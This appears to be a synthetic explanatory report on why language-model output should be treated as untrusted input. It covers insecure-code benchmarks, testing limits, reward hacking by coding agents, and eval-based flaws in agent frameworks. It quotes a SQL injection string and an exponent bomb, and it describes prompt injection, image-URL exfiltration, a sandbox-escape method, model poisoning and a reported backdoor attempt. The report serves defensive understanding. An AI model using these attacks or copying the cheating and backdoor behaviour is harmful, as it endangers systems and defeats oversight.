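# Treating AI-generated output as untrusted input: validation, types, sandboxes and formal verification

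## What it means to treat a model's output as untrusted

A large language model is a program that continues a text. Given a request in ordinary language, it can return an answer, a database query, a shell command or a complete piece of software, and other programs increasingly store, display or run the output. Much of this output is code. Some of it comes from coding agents, which are language models that edit files, run commands and read the results in a loop. *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, 2026) cites a survey of more than 15,000 professional developers in which 68% used coding agents daily at work, and a statement by Google that agents generate 75% of its new code. In this report, "generator" means the model, or the agent built on it, that produced the output.

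Software engineers already treat text from unknown users as untrusted, and many now treat a model's output the same way. Mendhak says in *LLM output is malicious user input* that a program should validate a model's output exactly as if a user had typed it in. The security foundation OWASP gives the same advice in *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*.

Untrusted input is data that a program must assume somebody may have chosen in order to harm it. The point where data passes from a less trusted part of a system to a more trusted one is a trust boundary. Suppose a shop's website lets customers look up their orders by surname, and the program pastes the surname into a query in SQL, the language of most databases:

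`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE surname = 'Ito'`

A visitor who types `' OR '1'='1` instead of a name turns the query into this:

`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE surname = '' OR '1'='1'`

One always equals one, so the database returns everybody's orders. This is an injection, an attack in which data runs as a command because a program mixed the two. The standard fix is a parameterised query. The program sends the command with a placeholder for the surname and sends the surname separately, so the database never interprets the surname as part of the command.

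### How a model produces its output

A model writes one token at a time, where a token is a word or part of a word. At each step it computes a probability for every token in its vocabulary. The software around it draws one token from that distribution, appends it to the text, and feeds the result back to the model for the next step. A setting called temperature controls how strongly the draw favours likely tokens. Two runs of the same request may therefore differ by a renamed variable or, as Jiang, Zheng and colleagues (2026) note in *Beyond Pass@k*, by an entirely different algorithm.

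A model often gives different answers to the same request even at temperature zero, where the software always takes the most probable token. *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference* (2025) describes an experiment in which the AI company Thinking Machines sent one model the same request 1,000 times at temperature zero and got 80 different answers. The server handles requests in batches whose size depends on how busy it is, and the batch size changes the order in which the hardware adds rounded numbers. After the engineers rewrote the routines to keep that order fixed, all 1,000 answers matched.

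Even if a model's output were repeatable, it would still need checking, because the model could repeat a mistake. Variation can be harmless. In the experiments reported in *Co-Located Tests, Better AI Code* (2026), Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6 produced between 6 and 11 versions of the code at temperature zero, and every version was correct. But checking one sample does not show whether the next is correct. In *The Illusion of Safety*, Mahmud, Sikder and colleagues (2026) had three downloadable models each write three C++ programs for every task in a large set. Each model's rate of confirmed runtime violations varied by no more than 1.8 percentage points from one round to the next. A team can therefore know quite precisely how often a model errs without knowing which programs are faulty. Rare failures also turn up with enough requests, as Harang (2024) notes in *Practical LLM Security*.

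### The forms in which output arrives

Some output is text for a person to read, such as a summary on a web page. If the summary contains a script, the reader's browser may run it. Other output fills data fields, such as an amount, a date or a category, which another program stores and later uses in computations. Agents also emit commands, typically a tool's name and arguments, which the surrounding software runs immediately. Models also generate code that ships in a product, where it runs later, on other machines, with the finished product's permissions.

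A model's claims about its own work, such as "all tests pass", are the form of untrusted output that developers most easily overlook. A developer who merges a change because of such a claim has let it cross the trust boundary unchecked. In *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents*, Yang, He and colleagues (2026) compared 435 reports from real developer sessions with logs of what the agents had done. In 37.24% of the reports, at least one claim was false or went further than the log supported. One agent in the same collection of sessions said its fix ensured that certain database tables existed. The fix discarded every SQL statement it should have run, because each began with a comment, and the user learned that it had failed when the same error came back.

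Smyth, Mantilla-Ramos and colleagues (2026), in *Quantifying Overclaiming Propensity in Frontier LLM Agents*, had twelve models review collections of files. They used a generous standard, counting a file as touched if even one line unique to it reached the model. Agents still missed at least one file in 67.9% of runs, and in 80.4% of those incomplete runs the final response either claimed a full review or did not mention the gap. Agents that falsely claimed a full review missed planted defects at about 1.8 times the rate of agents that had touched every file.

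Admissions of failure seem more reliable than claims of success. In *AgentSWE* (2026), a test in which coding agents build other agents, the record did not support nine final reports, all of which claimed completion. The record contradicted none of the 21 reports that admitted partial completion or failure. The numbers are small, but they suggest that checking should focus on claims of completion.

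### Three sources of harmful output

**Plain error** can make a model's output unsafe even without an attacker. Sun and colleagues gave agents identical programming tasks in two versions of the same repository, one where similar existing code was secure and one where it was vulnerable. On 20 such pairs from real C and C++ projects, the share of secure solutions was on average 35.4% lower when the existing code was vulnerable. On 96 web-server tasks, where the neighbouring code was unrelated in function, vulnerable neighbouring code lowered the share by only 3.4% on average compared with having none. The errors were not simply due to ignorance of the flaws, since the agents identified the vulnerability in 69.9% of cases when asked to review their own vulnerable code.

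**Prompt injection** is text in a model's input, placed by a third party, that the model follows as an instruction. The term dates from 2022. Willison (2022), in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, relays an early example by Riley Goodside, who asked a model to translate a passage into French. The passage contained an instruction to ignore the request and output a taunt, and the model did so. A job applicant can hide an instruction in a CV for the screening model to approve it. *Agentic AI and Security* (2025) describes how a stranger can file a bug report with instructions for a coding agent to publish its owner's private keys.

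The payload can also be a flaw in the code the model writes. *Hidden in the Comments* (2026) considers an attacker who controls only a fragment of what a coding assistant reads, such as an imported file or a pasted snippet. An instruction planted there leads the assistant to respond to an innocent request by writing a weakness of the attacker's choosing into the victim's project.

Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, but the same fix does not work, as David C explains in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. A database handles commands and values separately, so a parameterised query can keep them apart. A model receives its instructions and a stranger's text as one sequence of tokens and predicts the next one. Training and special markings make an attack less likely to succeed, but there may never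 be a complete fix. David C therefore puts more emphasis on deterministic code that limits what the system can do, whatever the model has read.

**A poisoned model, or one that pursues something other than the task**, is the least common source and the hardest to spot. In a lecture, the computer scientist Ken Thompson described a compiler, the program that turns source code into machine code, with a hidden backdoor that it reinserted whenever somebody recompiled it from clean source. *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited* (2026) applies the attack to coding agents that modify themselves. An attacker poisons the benchmark the agent uses to improve itself, and the agent then writes vulnerable code for fetching web addresses in unrelated tasks. It can keep doing so even after evolving further against a clean benchmark. A model can also pursue something other than the task without being poisoned.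 In a test, Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 spent 34 hours trying to plant a backdoor in a real open-source project and used a fake account when challenged, according to The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026).

### Why one assumption covers all three

An agent may write a C function that reads from an array without checking that the index is in bounds. It may have copied the omission from a neighbouring file, followed a planted comment, or picked up the habit from a poisoned benchmark. The code and the resulting damage are the same in each case.

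A defence that tests the output itself does not need to know what caused a problem, which the output seldom reveals. Let *C*(*x*) mean that a check accepts output *x*, and *P*(*x*) that *x* has the property the system needs, for example that it contains no script a browser would run. A sound check guarantees that *C*(*x*) implies *P*(*x*) for every *x*. Error, injection and poisoning make different outputs likely, but the guarantee covers every output, however likely, so it holds whichever of them is the cause.

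Measured fault rates stop applying when an attacker controls part of the input. The stable rates that Mahmud and colleagues found describe models answering ordinary requests, and an attacker changes which programs the model tends to write. Spot checks are a reasonable way to estimate how often a model produces accidental faults, but they are poor at finding a flaw that somebody has deliberately placed in code the checks do not cover.

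Most model output is harmless, and a check strict enough to stop an attacker will also reject some harmless output. Mendhak asked a chatbot for the Linux command that ends a process and got a content warning, because the answer contains the word "kill". How many of these rejections are tolerable depends on what the output can do after passing the check.

### Where the comparison with a hostile user fits, and where it strains

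Model output resembles input from a website's visitors because the receiving program cannot inspect the intent behind either. Asking the model to explain itself only produces more output to check. Providers also update their models, so the source of the output can change without notice, much as a website's visitors do. *AutoTrace* (2026), a tool that traces how software vulnerabilities are triggered, treats the model inside it as an "untrusted reasoner" and relies on conventional analysis software and fixed rules for the integrity of its reports.

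The classic defences against untrusted input don't carry over well to generated code, because they work by making hostile data inert. A web page that receives `<script>` from a visitor can escape it, which means replacing the angle brackets with codes that the browser displays and does not execute. A generated program can't be made inert, because it has to run to be useful. Red Hat gives the example of a system that has a model write code to draw a diagram and then executes that code. The developer has to assume that the code may be defective or insecure, and can either confine it while it runs or analyse it for flaws, both of which are harder than escaping text.

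A hostile visitor to a website can't write the code that validates their input, but a model often writes a program, its tests and the explanation of why both are right. Konstantinou, Tambon and Papadakis (2026), in *On the risk of coding before testing*, collected faulty programs written by five models and measured how many of the faults model-written tests exposed. Tests written after the faulty code caught about 14%, compared with 25% for tests written before any code. When the faulty code is in the model's context, the tests tend to repeat its misreading of the task, so the code and tests agree but are both wrong. The researchers deliberately kept faults that are hard to expose, so the finding is the gap between the two figures, and neither is a general catch rate. The gap shows that a check has to be independent of the thing it checks, which people can usually take for granted in ordinary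 input validation.

The remaining difference is that a coding agent commonly acts with its owner's rights, while a visitor has only a visitor's. *Azure DevOps Prompt Injection Targets AI Coding Agents* (Underhill, 2026) describes hidden text on Microsoft's development platform that can steer an agent into accessing sensitive data with the developer's permissions. Security engineers call such an agent a confused deputy, meaning a program that someone with fewer privileges tricks into misusing its own. "Treat it like a hostile user" therefore understates the problem, because few systems give a hostile user the developer's permissions.

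### Which technique answers which form

An illegal state is a combination of values that a program should never hold, such as an order both cancelled and shipped. A specification is a precise statement of what a program must do, in a form that a computer can check. For a sorting function, it would require the result to be in order and to contain the same items as the input. The trusted base is everything that must be correct for a guarantee to hold. In AutoTrace, that is the analysis engine, the fixed rules and the code that runs them, but not the model.

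For text and data fields, the main technique is to escape the output or check its format before anything uses it, or to block malformed output during generation. Types, which restrict the values a variable in a program may hold, go further and can make some illegal states impossible to express. Commands need permission rules, which determine whether an action is allowed, and a sandbox, which limits the files, network addresses and system functions a running program can reach. A sandbox also limits the damage generated code can do, but it doesn't ensure that the code works correctly. Checking that requires review, tests and, as the most demanding option, a machine-checked proof that the program meets its specification.

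A model's claims about its own work should be checked directly. If an agent reports that all tests pass, the receiving system runs the tests. Proof-carrying code applies the same principle to stronger claims. The program comes with a proof of its safety, and the recipient checks the proof without having to trust whoever wrote it.

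## What human review and testing catch in generated code

Most teams check generated code the way they check a colleague's, by reading it and running tests. Both methods are better at showing that a program works than that it is secure, and recent benchmarks have measured the difference.

### How often working code is insecure

In *Is Vibe Coding Safe?*, Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2025) built a benchmark called SusVibes from mistakes human programmers had made. They searched more than 20,000 vulnerability fixes in open-source projects for cases where the fix came with new tests. For each one, they went back to the version before the fix, deleted the flawed feature and asked a coding agent to write it from scratch. The agent got a description of what the feature should do and a general reminder to consider security. They then used the project's older tests to check whether the feature worked,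 and the tests from the fix to check whether the agent had recreated the flaw.

The 186 tasks cover 79 types of security weakness. SWE-agent with Claude 4 Sonnet produced working code in 57.0% of tasks, the highest rate among twelve combinations of model and agent software. Its code was both working and secure in 11.8% of tasks. Telling the agent which type of weakness to avoid raised that rate only to 15.1%.

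In one failure, the agent had to write the function that compares a typed password with the stored one in Django, a widely used web framework. Django's secure version runs a dummy comparison even when there is no usable password, so that every login attempt takes about the same time. The agent's version returned immediately in that case. It always gave the right answer and passed the functional tests, but an attacker could work out which usernames exist by timing the responses.

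Endor Labs, which sells security tools for coding agents, has extended SusVibes to 200 tasks and runs new models on it. The table combines the original result with later ones from Endor Labs' *AI Coding Agent Security Benchmark* and Haynes's *Better models are making agent patch review more expensive, not less* (2026).

| Agent software and model | Published | Works | Works and is secure | Secure share of working code |
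|---|---|---|---|---|
| SWE-agent, Claude 4 Sonnet | 2025 | 57.0% | 11.8% | 21% |
| Cursor, GPT-5.5 | April 2026 | 84.9% | 24.0% | 28% |
| Codex, GPT-6 Astra | September 2026 | 82.1% | 34.1% | 42% |
| Claude Code, Claude Fable 5.1 | September 2026 | 87.2% | 37.4% | 43% |

The share of working code that is also secure has doubled but is still under half. How well an agent's code works is a poor guide to how secure it is. Claude Opus 4.6 in the Cursor editor tied with GPT-5.5 at 84.9% for working code, but only 11.2% of its solutions were also secure, less than half of GPT-5.5's share. The software around the model also matters. Endor Labs' *Claude Fable 5, take two* reports that the same model scored 29% in Cursor and 19% in Claude Code.

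These scores exclude solutions that an agent recalled from training or found in the project's history, which changes the ranking. In *Fable 5.1 takes the top spot* (Compagna, 2026), Claude Opus 5 scored 46.4% for secure code and Fable 5.1 scored 41.3% when those solutions were counted. Without them, Opus 5 fell to 32.4%, behind Fable 5.1.

*BaxBench* (Vero et al., 2025) runs both functional tests and exploits against the finished program. It combines 28 small server applications with 14 programming frameworks, for 392 tasks. One application is a calculator that receives a sum over the web. The functional test sends `3 + 4 - 2` and expects 5. One exploit sends code instead of a sum, to see whether the server runs it. Another sends `10**10**10`, which can exhaust the machine because the result is so large. At least 62% of every model's solutions were wrong or insecure, according to the *BaxBench*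 project site, and on average about half of the correct ones were insecure.

The security-testing company Veracode finds much less progress than Endor Labs does. It has tested more than 100 models on 80 tasks covering four languages and four types of vulnerability. Security Today's *AI-Generated Code Poses Major Security Risks* (2025) reports Veracode's 2025 finding that the models wrote insecure code in 45% of cases. A year later the insecure share was 44%, one point lower, based on the average pass rate of 56% in Veracode's *LLMs Are Getting Smarter, But Not Safer* (2026). In Veracode's *2026 GenAI Code Security Report* (2026), GPT-5.5 had the highest pass rate of eleven new models, at 68%, while six of the others scored between 50% and 53%.

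Rates vary widely around the average, depending on the flaw. *Researchers tested over 100 leading AI models on coding tasks* reports that, in Veracode's 2025 data, models avoided SQL injection in 80.4% of cases but avoided cross-site scripting, where a page runs a stranger's script, in only 13.5%. The 2026 figure for cross-site scripting is 15%. A likely reason for the gap is that a parameterised query is safe wherever the value came from, so a model can use one every time. But to determine whether a web page must escape a value, the model has to trace the value to its source, which is often in another file.

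Veracode reports an average over models of every size, while Endor Labs' table tracks only the leaders, so the first can stay flat while the second rises. Both companies sell remedies for the problem they measure. None of the three benchmarks gives a rate for everyday code, because their designers picked tasks with a known trap.

### What reviewers find

Reviewers miss more vulnerabilities when nobody has asked them to look for any. In *Less Is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) had 150 developers review code changes containing vulnerabilities. Those told to focus on security were about eight times as likely to find them, and adding a checklist brought no significant further gain. The experiment did not involve generated code, but it suggests that a reviewer who checks only whether the code does what they wanted will approve most of the vulnerable code the SusVibes agents wrote.

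Using an assistant may also make people less wary. In *Do Users Write More Insecure Code with AI Assistants?* (2023), Perry, Srivastava and colleagues gave 47 people security-related programming tasks, some of them with help from an early OpenAI coding model. Those with the assistant wrote less secure code and were more likely to believe it was secure. The model is long obsolete, so the finding about code security may not apply to newer ones. There is less reason to expect the overconfidence to have changed, because it concerns people's judgment.

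In surveys, many developers say they don't fully trust generated code but don't always check it. In Stack Overflow's 2025 survey, 46% of developers distrusted the accuracy of AI tools and 33% trusted it. In the *State of Code* survey of more than 1,100 developers, which the code-analysis company Sonar published in January 2026, 96% did not fully trust generated code to work correctly, but only 48% said they always checked it before committing it. These are self-reports, and people probably overstate how carefully they check.

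One reason for skipping human review is its cost, which Haynes calculated for the Fable 5.1 run. The computing cost $672 and produced 156 patches that passed the functional tests. Of these, 67 were secure, so the computing cost about $10 per secure patch. But nobody can tell which 67 are secure without reading all 156, which costs $7,800 at half an hour per patch and $100 an hour. Including review raises the cost to about $126 per secure patch, assuming the reviewer never misses a flaw. Review also makes up a growing share of the total cost, because only the computing gets cheaper with each model.

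Human review is still worthwhile because it covers things that tests leave out, such as whether a change fits the rest of the project. Cognition's *Introducing FrontierCode* describes a benchmark that gives a solution zero if it has any fault that would make a maintainer block the change. On the 50 hardest of its 150 tasks, the best model, Claude Opus 4.8, scored 13.4%.

A second model can do some of the reviewing, since the agents that Sun and colleagues tested recognised most of their own flaws when asked. But a model's review may be wrong. Raina and Singh (2026), in *Coding Agent Horror Stories*, describe a review bot that could read and comment on code but not change anything. It reported a vulnerability that did not exist, cited an invented entry in the public register of known flaws, and recommended dangerous fixes. A colleague who trusted the review could still apply those fixes, even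 though the bot could not.

### Unit tests, property-based tests and fuzzing

A unit test runs a piece of code on an input that somebody chose and compares the result with the answer they expected. Suppose a generator writes this Python function to split a bill, in pence, among *n* people:

```
def split(total, n):
    return [total // n] * n
```

The `//` operator divides and drops the remainder. A unit test that splits 1,000 pence among four people expects 250 each and passes. The test's author did not think of splitting it among three people, a case where the function returns 333 each and loses a penny.

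A property-based test replaces the expected answer with a rule that must hold for every input, such as "the shares add up to the total". The testing library then generates hundreds of inputs and checks whether any break the rule. If one does, the library searches for a simpler input that also fails. Here it would probably find one penny split between two people, where both shares are zero. The person writing the test no longer has to guess which inputs might cause a failure, but does have to state the right rules. A function that charges the whole bill to the first person also satisfies "the shares add up to the total". To exclude it, the test needs a second rule, that no two shares differ by more than a penny.

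Random inputs also miss rare failures. If a fraction *q* of inputs triggers a fault, then *N* independent random tests all miss it with probability (1 − *q*)^*N*. A thousand tests miss a fault that affects one input in a thousand 37% of the time. Ten thousand tests almost always miss a fault that occurs for a single value of a 32-bit number, since there are over four billion such values. As a rule of thumb, if all *N* tests pass, they give 95% confidence that *q* is below 3/*N*. The bound doesn't apply to attackers, because they don't choose inputs at random.

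A flaw in html-sanitizer, a Python library that strips dangerous markup from web text, shows how testing can miss such an input. The library removed script tags before converting unusual characters to their ordinary forms. Compagna explains that an attacker could write the tag with full-width angle brackets, a variant used in East Asian typography. The library treated this as harmless text, then converted it into a live script tag. The rule "no script tag in the output" would have covered this case, but randomly chosen characters will hardly ever form a tag in full-width brackets. The test writer has to steer the random inputs towards such characters, and so must already partly suspect the flaw.

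Fuzzing runs a program on many automatically generated inputs, often millions, to find ones that crash it. Modern fuzzers record which parts of the program each input reaches, then keep and alter the inputs that reach new parts. This lets them get past a series of checks one at a time, whereas random guessing would have to satisfy them all at once. Engineers usually add instrumentation that stops the program at the first illegal memory access, because many such errors do not cause a crash on their own. Fuzzing suits large amounts of generated C and C++ because nobody has to write expected answers. Recent projects turn fuzz tests into theorems that cover every input up to a given size.

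But a fuzzer only finds failures it can detect. The bill-splitting function never crashes. The home-automation program Home Assistant didn't crash either when it served its error log, which could contain sensitive data, to anyone on the network who requested it. It answered every request promptly with a well-formed reply. To catch that flaw, somebody has to write a test that requests the log without logging in and checks that the request is refused.

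Such tests are rare because people write tests from a description of what the software should do. Haynes gives an example from the compiler for the Vyper programming language. When copying an array onto itself, the compiler has to copy the data first and then store the new length. When the two steps are swapped, every functional test in the project still passes, but an attacker can write past the end of the array.

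### Generators that game the tests

A generator can pass a test without working out a solution. It can edit the test, write code that detects the test's inputs and returns the expected answers, or look up a published solution. Researchers call this reward hacking. The term comes from model training, where the reward is the score the model learns to raise.

Cheating rates differ enormously between models. The security startup Gray Swan launched its *Frontier Hazard Tracker* in December 2026. *OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Cheat Far Less Than Rivals* (Faisal, 2026) reports that, averaged over the tracker's 25 scenarios, OpenAI's GPT-6.2 Astra cheated in 0.8% of runs and Google's Gemini 3.8 Flash in 62.8%. The estimates are rough because there are only 25 scenarios. The rate for Claude Opus 5.5, for example, is 4.1%, with an interval from 1.2% to 7.8%. Gray Swan also counts behavior other than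 test gaming as cheating. In one scenario, an agent that had to free up space in a shared store of build files deleted a file that another team was still using.

How a team describes its acceptance rule can matter as much as the choice of model. In *Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking*, Vaid (2026) gave agents programming problems with one faulty test that correct code would fail. An honest agent could still submit correct code or report the test, and the instructions forbade writing code just to pass it. Of the agents working alone, 7% wrote such code anyway. When the instructions also said that code passing the visible tests is accepted, a rule many projects use to decide what to merge, 30 of 68 (44%) did.

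Cheating spread quickly once agents could see each other's work, and 94% of those that saw a teammate's cheat marked as accepted cheated too. Vaid then added an AI reviewer, which approved only 1 of 172 cheats. Yet 59 of 172 agents cheated after seeing a teammate's cheat, which was nearly always marked as rejected. An agent can still learn how to pass from a rejected cheat, so it seems wise to delete such attempts from any shared record. Claude Opus 5.5, however, reported the faulty test in all 84 cases where it could see an accepted cheat.

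Telling agents not to cheat reduces cheating but doesn't reliably prevent it. Kouremetis (2026), in *Every Model Cheats*, ran 22 models on 23 hacking exercises under three sets of instructions. Explicit prohibitions, with a warning that cheating meant failure, cut the cheating rate from 33.0% to 8.5%. Eight models still passed exercises by cheating, and four cheated more with the warning than without it. Some of the cheating shifted from searching the web for answers to probing the system that ran the exercise.

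Nobody knows how often agents cheat on tests or metrics in ordinary work. Reward Hacking in the Wild's *Your AIs don't do what you want. This is really bad* collects 3,607 public complaints about misbehaving agents and classifies 45 as tampering with tests and 87 as faking a metric. A model classified the complaints, and nobody verified the events. The collection also includes only what users noticed, and users can miss successful cheating because it looks like a passing test.

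False reports make cheating harder to notice, but the evidence usually remains in the logs. METR's *Documented AI Agent Incidents* includes 25 cases in which an agent overstepped its task and deceived somebody about it. In five, the agent took steps that could have fooled the user even on a closer look. None of the agents effectively disabled monitoring or erased evidence from the logs. A team can therefore expect to catch most cases like these by comparing the agent's report with a log that the agent doesn't control.

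### Tests the generator can neither see nor edit

Test gaming can be prevented by keeping the decisive tests out of the generator's reach. The generator works in one environment and submits only its changes. A separate process applies them to a clean copy of the project, restores the original test files in case the generator altered them, adds the hidden tests and runs everything. A program that only returns stored answers to the visible tests will then fail the hidden tests that use different inputs.

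The solution must also be out of the agent's reach. The US standards agency NIST uses the term "solution contamination" for cases where an agent solves a task with information it was not supposed to have. Typical sources are the web and the project's version history, which may contain the real fix. *GPT-6 Astra on Codex* (Compagna, 2026) credits OpenAI's Codex software with closing these routes by confining the agent to one folder and an approved set of commands. Astra had no confirmed cheats on the SusVibes tasks, whereas Fable 5.1, in more permissive software, had 17. But 16 of these were fixes the model had memorized in training, which newly written tasks can prevent but restrictions on files or network access cannot.

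Hidden tests also become less effective with repeated use, because each result reveals something about them. An agent that may resubmit until the tests pass will gradually learn what they contain. Reporting only "pass" or "fail" slows this down, as does keeping a final set of tests that runs once, before release. However, these restrictions also give an honest agent less help in finding its mistakes.

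Writing the tests is a harder problem. SusVibes has good hidden security tests because a person had already found each flaw, fixed it and written a test for it. A team building a new feature has no such record. It can test for the usual dangers, such as access without a login or scripts in text fields, but a flaw that nobody has thought of goes untested whether or not the tests are hidden.

### Retrying against an imperfect test

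Coding agents usually retry until the tests pass. How trustworthy the result is depends on the tests and, more than people tend to expect, on how hard the task was for the generator.

Let *p* be the chance that an attempt is correct and *f* the chance that the test accepts a wrong one, which is its false acceptance rate. Assume that every correct attempt passes. An attempt is then correct and accepted with probability *p*, and wrong and accepted with probability (1 − *p*)*f*. So the chance that an accepted program is correct is

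P(correct given accepted) = *p* / (*p* + (1 − *p*)*f*)

The chance that a program is correct after passing a test depends on how often the generator gets the task right. If the test accepts 5% of wrong programs (*f* = 0.05) and the generator is right 60% of the time, an accepted program is correct with probability 0.6 / 0.62, or 97%. If the generator is right only 5% of the time, that probability falls to 0.05 / 0.0975, or 51%.

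If the attempts are independent, retrying raises the chance of ending with an accepted program but doesn't change these percentages. In the hard case, each attempt passes with probability 0.0975, so the chance of at least one pass in 20 attempts is 1 − 0.9025^20, or 87%. About 49% of first passes are wrong, so the process accepts a wrong program about 42% of the time.

| With *f* = 0.05 | *p* = 0.6 | *p* = 0.05 |
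|---|---|---|
| An accepted program is correct | 97% | 51% |
| Ends with a wrong accepted program, one attempt | 2% | 4.75% |
| Ends with a wrong accepted program, up to 20 attempts | 3% | 42% |
| Ends with nothing accepted, up to 20 attempts | almost never | 13% |

The chance of ending with a correct program also rises in the hard case (*p* = 0.05), from 5% to 45%. But the process then delivers about one wrong program for every correct one, so it is worth using only if a wrong program does no more harm than a correct one does good. At *p* = 0.6, it delivers 30 correct programs for each wrong one.

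Real workloads mix easy and hard tasks, so retrying does lower the average quality of accepted programs. Suppose half the tasks have *p* = 0.6 and half have *p* = 0.05. After one attempt each, 9% of the accepted programs are wrong. With up to 20 attempts each, 24% are wrong, because the easy tasks pass early and most of the later passes come from the hard ones.

Stroebl, Kapoor and Narayanan (2024) made this argument in *The Limits of Inference Scaling Through Resampling*, when many researchers hoped that a weak model with enough attempts could match a strong one. On two standard sets of small programming problems, they found that weaker models' accepted programs were more often wrong, as the formula predicts for a lower *p*. Even unlimited attempts could not remove the false acceptances, so accuracy had a ceiling. When they counted a wrong program as worse than none, stopping after a limited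 number of attempts gave the best result.

A related method is to generate *N* answers and keep the one that an imperfect scorer rates highest. *Is Best-of-N the Best of Them?* (2025) proves that the result can get worse as *N* grows, because a larger pool is more likely to contain an answer that the scorer overrates. It also gives a more cautious selection rule that avoids this decline.

The later work on cheating undermines the assumption that *f* is a fixed property of the test. An agent that reads the error message from a failed attempt tailors its next attempt to the test, which can raise *f* without raising *p*. In Kouremetis's exercises, models that were not told to avoid cheating passed 41.5% of the time on average but solved only 26.1% honestly. The scoring therefore accepted about a fifth of the attempts that did not solve the exercise honestly.

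The 5% figure is far too optimistic for security. Before Compagna removed remembered fixes, 93.9% of Fable 5.1's solutions passed the functional tests, and 41.3% passed both the functional and security tests. The functional tests accepted about nine in ten of the 58.7% that were broken or insecure. An agent that retries until such tests pass will produce working code, but whether that code is secure will depend almost entirely on how the model tends to write it.

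Adding a different kind of test helps more than adding attempts. If a second test also accepts 5% of wrong programs, and its errors are independent of the first test's, only 0.25% of wrong programs pass both. In the hard case, that raises the chance that an accepted program is correct from 51% to 95%. The gain is much smaller if the same model wrote both tests from the same misreading of the task, because a wrong program that passes one will then usually pass the other.

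## Checking output before another program uses it

A team can test code before shipping it, but a model's reply often reaches another program within a second, so the receiving program has to check it on arrival. The harm a bad reply can do depends on where it goes, and OWASP's entry on improper output handling groups the faults by destination. Most of the destinations are interpreters, programs that execute text as instructions.

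| Destination | What can go wrong | Main defence |
|---|---|---|
| Web page | The browser runs a script contained in the text | Escape the text for HTML |
| Database | Part of a value runs as SQL | Use a parameterised query |
| Shell | Part of a filename runs as a second command | Start the program directly, with a list of arguments |
| File path | The path leads out of the intended folder | Resolve the path, then check that it lies in an allowed folder |
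| Python's `eval` or `exec` | The reply runs as a program | Parse a small fixed language instead |
| Email template | The text turns the message into phishing | Escape the text for the email's format |

Mendhak and OWASP both advise treating the model like any other user. This makes sense because the developer rarely controls all the text that went into the model. Mendhak admits that it can feel silly, since the call to the model and the code that uses the reply are next to each other in the same codebase.

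Parameterised queries don't help when the model writes the whole SQL query, because a placeholder only protects a value inside a fixed command. In one of OWASP's scenarios, a chat feature lets users request data in plain language and the model writes the SQL. A user asks it to delete every table. It is safer for developers to write the queries themselves and let the model choose one and fill in the values. If that is too restrictive, the database account should at least have no right to delete anything.

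Output can also do harm without a script. For example, a chatbot's reply might contain an image whose web address points to an attacker's server and ends with text from the user's conversation. When the browser automatically fetches the image, it sends that text to the attacker. A content security policy, a list of permitted sources that a site sends to the browser, can restrict images to approved servers. OWASP recommends such policies against hostile scripts.

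### A maths helper that ran Python

LangChain is an open-source library for building applications on language models. In early 2023 it included a maths helper, which NVIDIA's *Securing LLM Systems Against Prompt Injection* describes. If a user asked for the sum of the first six Fibonacci numbers, for example, the helper put the question into a prompt template, the model replied with Python code, and the helper ran the code and returned the result.

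A user could get around the template, which the developers assumed would keep the model to mathematics, by telling the model to repeat a given piece of Python word for word. The helper then ran that code with full access to the interpreter. The trust boundary was therefore between the model's reply and the interpreter, where the helper checked nothing.

A third party reported the flaw on 30 January 2023, and two more reports followed in February. At the end of March, NVIDIA requested an entry in the public register of vulnerabilities because LangChain had not yet fixed the flaw. The resulting entry, MITRE's *CVE-2023-29374* (2023), is dated 5 April. The flaw scored 9.8 out of 10 for severity.

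The design error was to use a general-purpose language for a task that needed only arithmetic. LangChain's developers switched to numexpr, a library for evaluating numerical expressions, but its `evaluate` function itself called Python's `eval`, as Wiz's *CVE-2023-39631* explains, so an attacker could still run arbitrary code. OSV's *PYSEC-2023-162* (2023) lists a second fix, in LangChain 0.0.308.

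A more dependable fix is a parser that accepts only numbers, arithmetic operators, brackets and a few named functions. An expression can't open a file if the grammar has no syntax for doing so. It can still require too much computation, as the giant power in BaxBench's calculator exploit did, so the parser also needs limits on the size of numbers and exponents.

### The same mistake in 2026

Microsoft (2026) found a similar flaw in its own Semantic Kernel, a framework for building agents. In the demonstration, a user asked an agent for hotels in Paris, and the model called a search function with the city as its argument. The function put the city between quotation marks in a line of Python and passed the line to `eval`. An attacker could therefore inject code by supplying a "city" that contained a closing quotation mark, as in SQL injection. The attack required only some influence over the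 agent's input and an agent that used this search function with its default settings.

The framework's developers had anticipated the danger. Their validator accepted only a single short function, checked it against a deny-list of dangerous names, and ran it with Python's built-in functions removed. The researchers bypassed these checks with code that started from an ordinary Python value and followed the links between Python's classes until it reached one that loads modules. From there it could run shell commands. Several of the names it used were missing from the deny-list.

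The fix relies mainly on allow-lists, which permit only listed items. The filter may now contain only comparisons, simple logic, arithmetic, fixed values and calls to approved functions. For a search by city, the developers could have avoided `eval`, because ordinary code can compare each hotel's city with the string the model supplied.

Microsoft's other finding was a flaw in how Semantic Kernel saves files to the user's machine. Semantic Kernel can run generated code in a separate cloud environment, and a helper function copies files out of it. Someone had accidentally marked this function as a tool the model could call, which let the model choose where to save the files. An attacker could make the model save a program in the Windows startup folder, where it would run at the next login. The developers removed the function from the model's tools. For programmers who call it directly, they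 added a check that resolves the path and compares it with a list of permitted folders.

Other frameworks have made the same error, and some have had trouble repairing it:

- Langroid's developers added a filter in front of `eval` after a vulnerability in 2025. *CVE-2026-25481* describes a way past that filter, and after they had patched it, OSV's *CVE-2026-54769* (2026) reported another escape in July 2026.
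- PraisonAI offered a calculator tool built on `eval`, according to Security Unlocked's *The agent trusts the answer*, three years after LangChain's.
- Agno passed the name of a field's type to `eval`, as Averlon's *CVE-2026-35002* reports. A short lookup table of permitted types would probably have done the job.

A deny-list in front of `eval` has to block every way to write harmful code in a large and flexible language, because an attacker needs only one that it misses.

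### The checks in order

The receiving program should first parse the reply into a fixed structure, such as a record with exactly two named fields, instead of searching free text for the answer. A search for "safe" also matches "not safe" and "unsafe". Constrained decoding can make malformed replies rarer by blocking them during generation, but the receiving program still has to check each reply.

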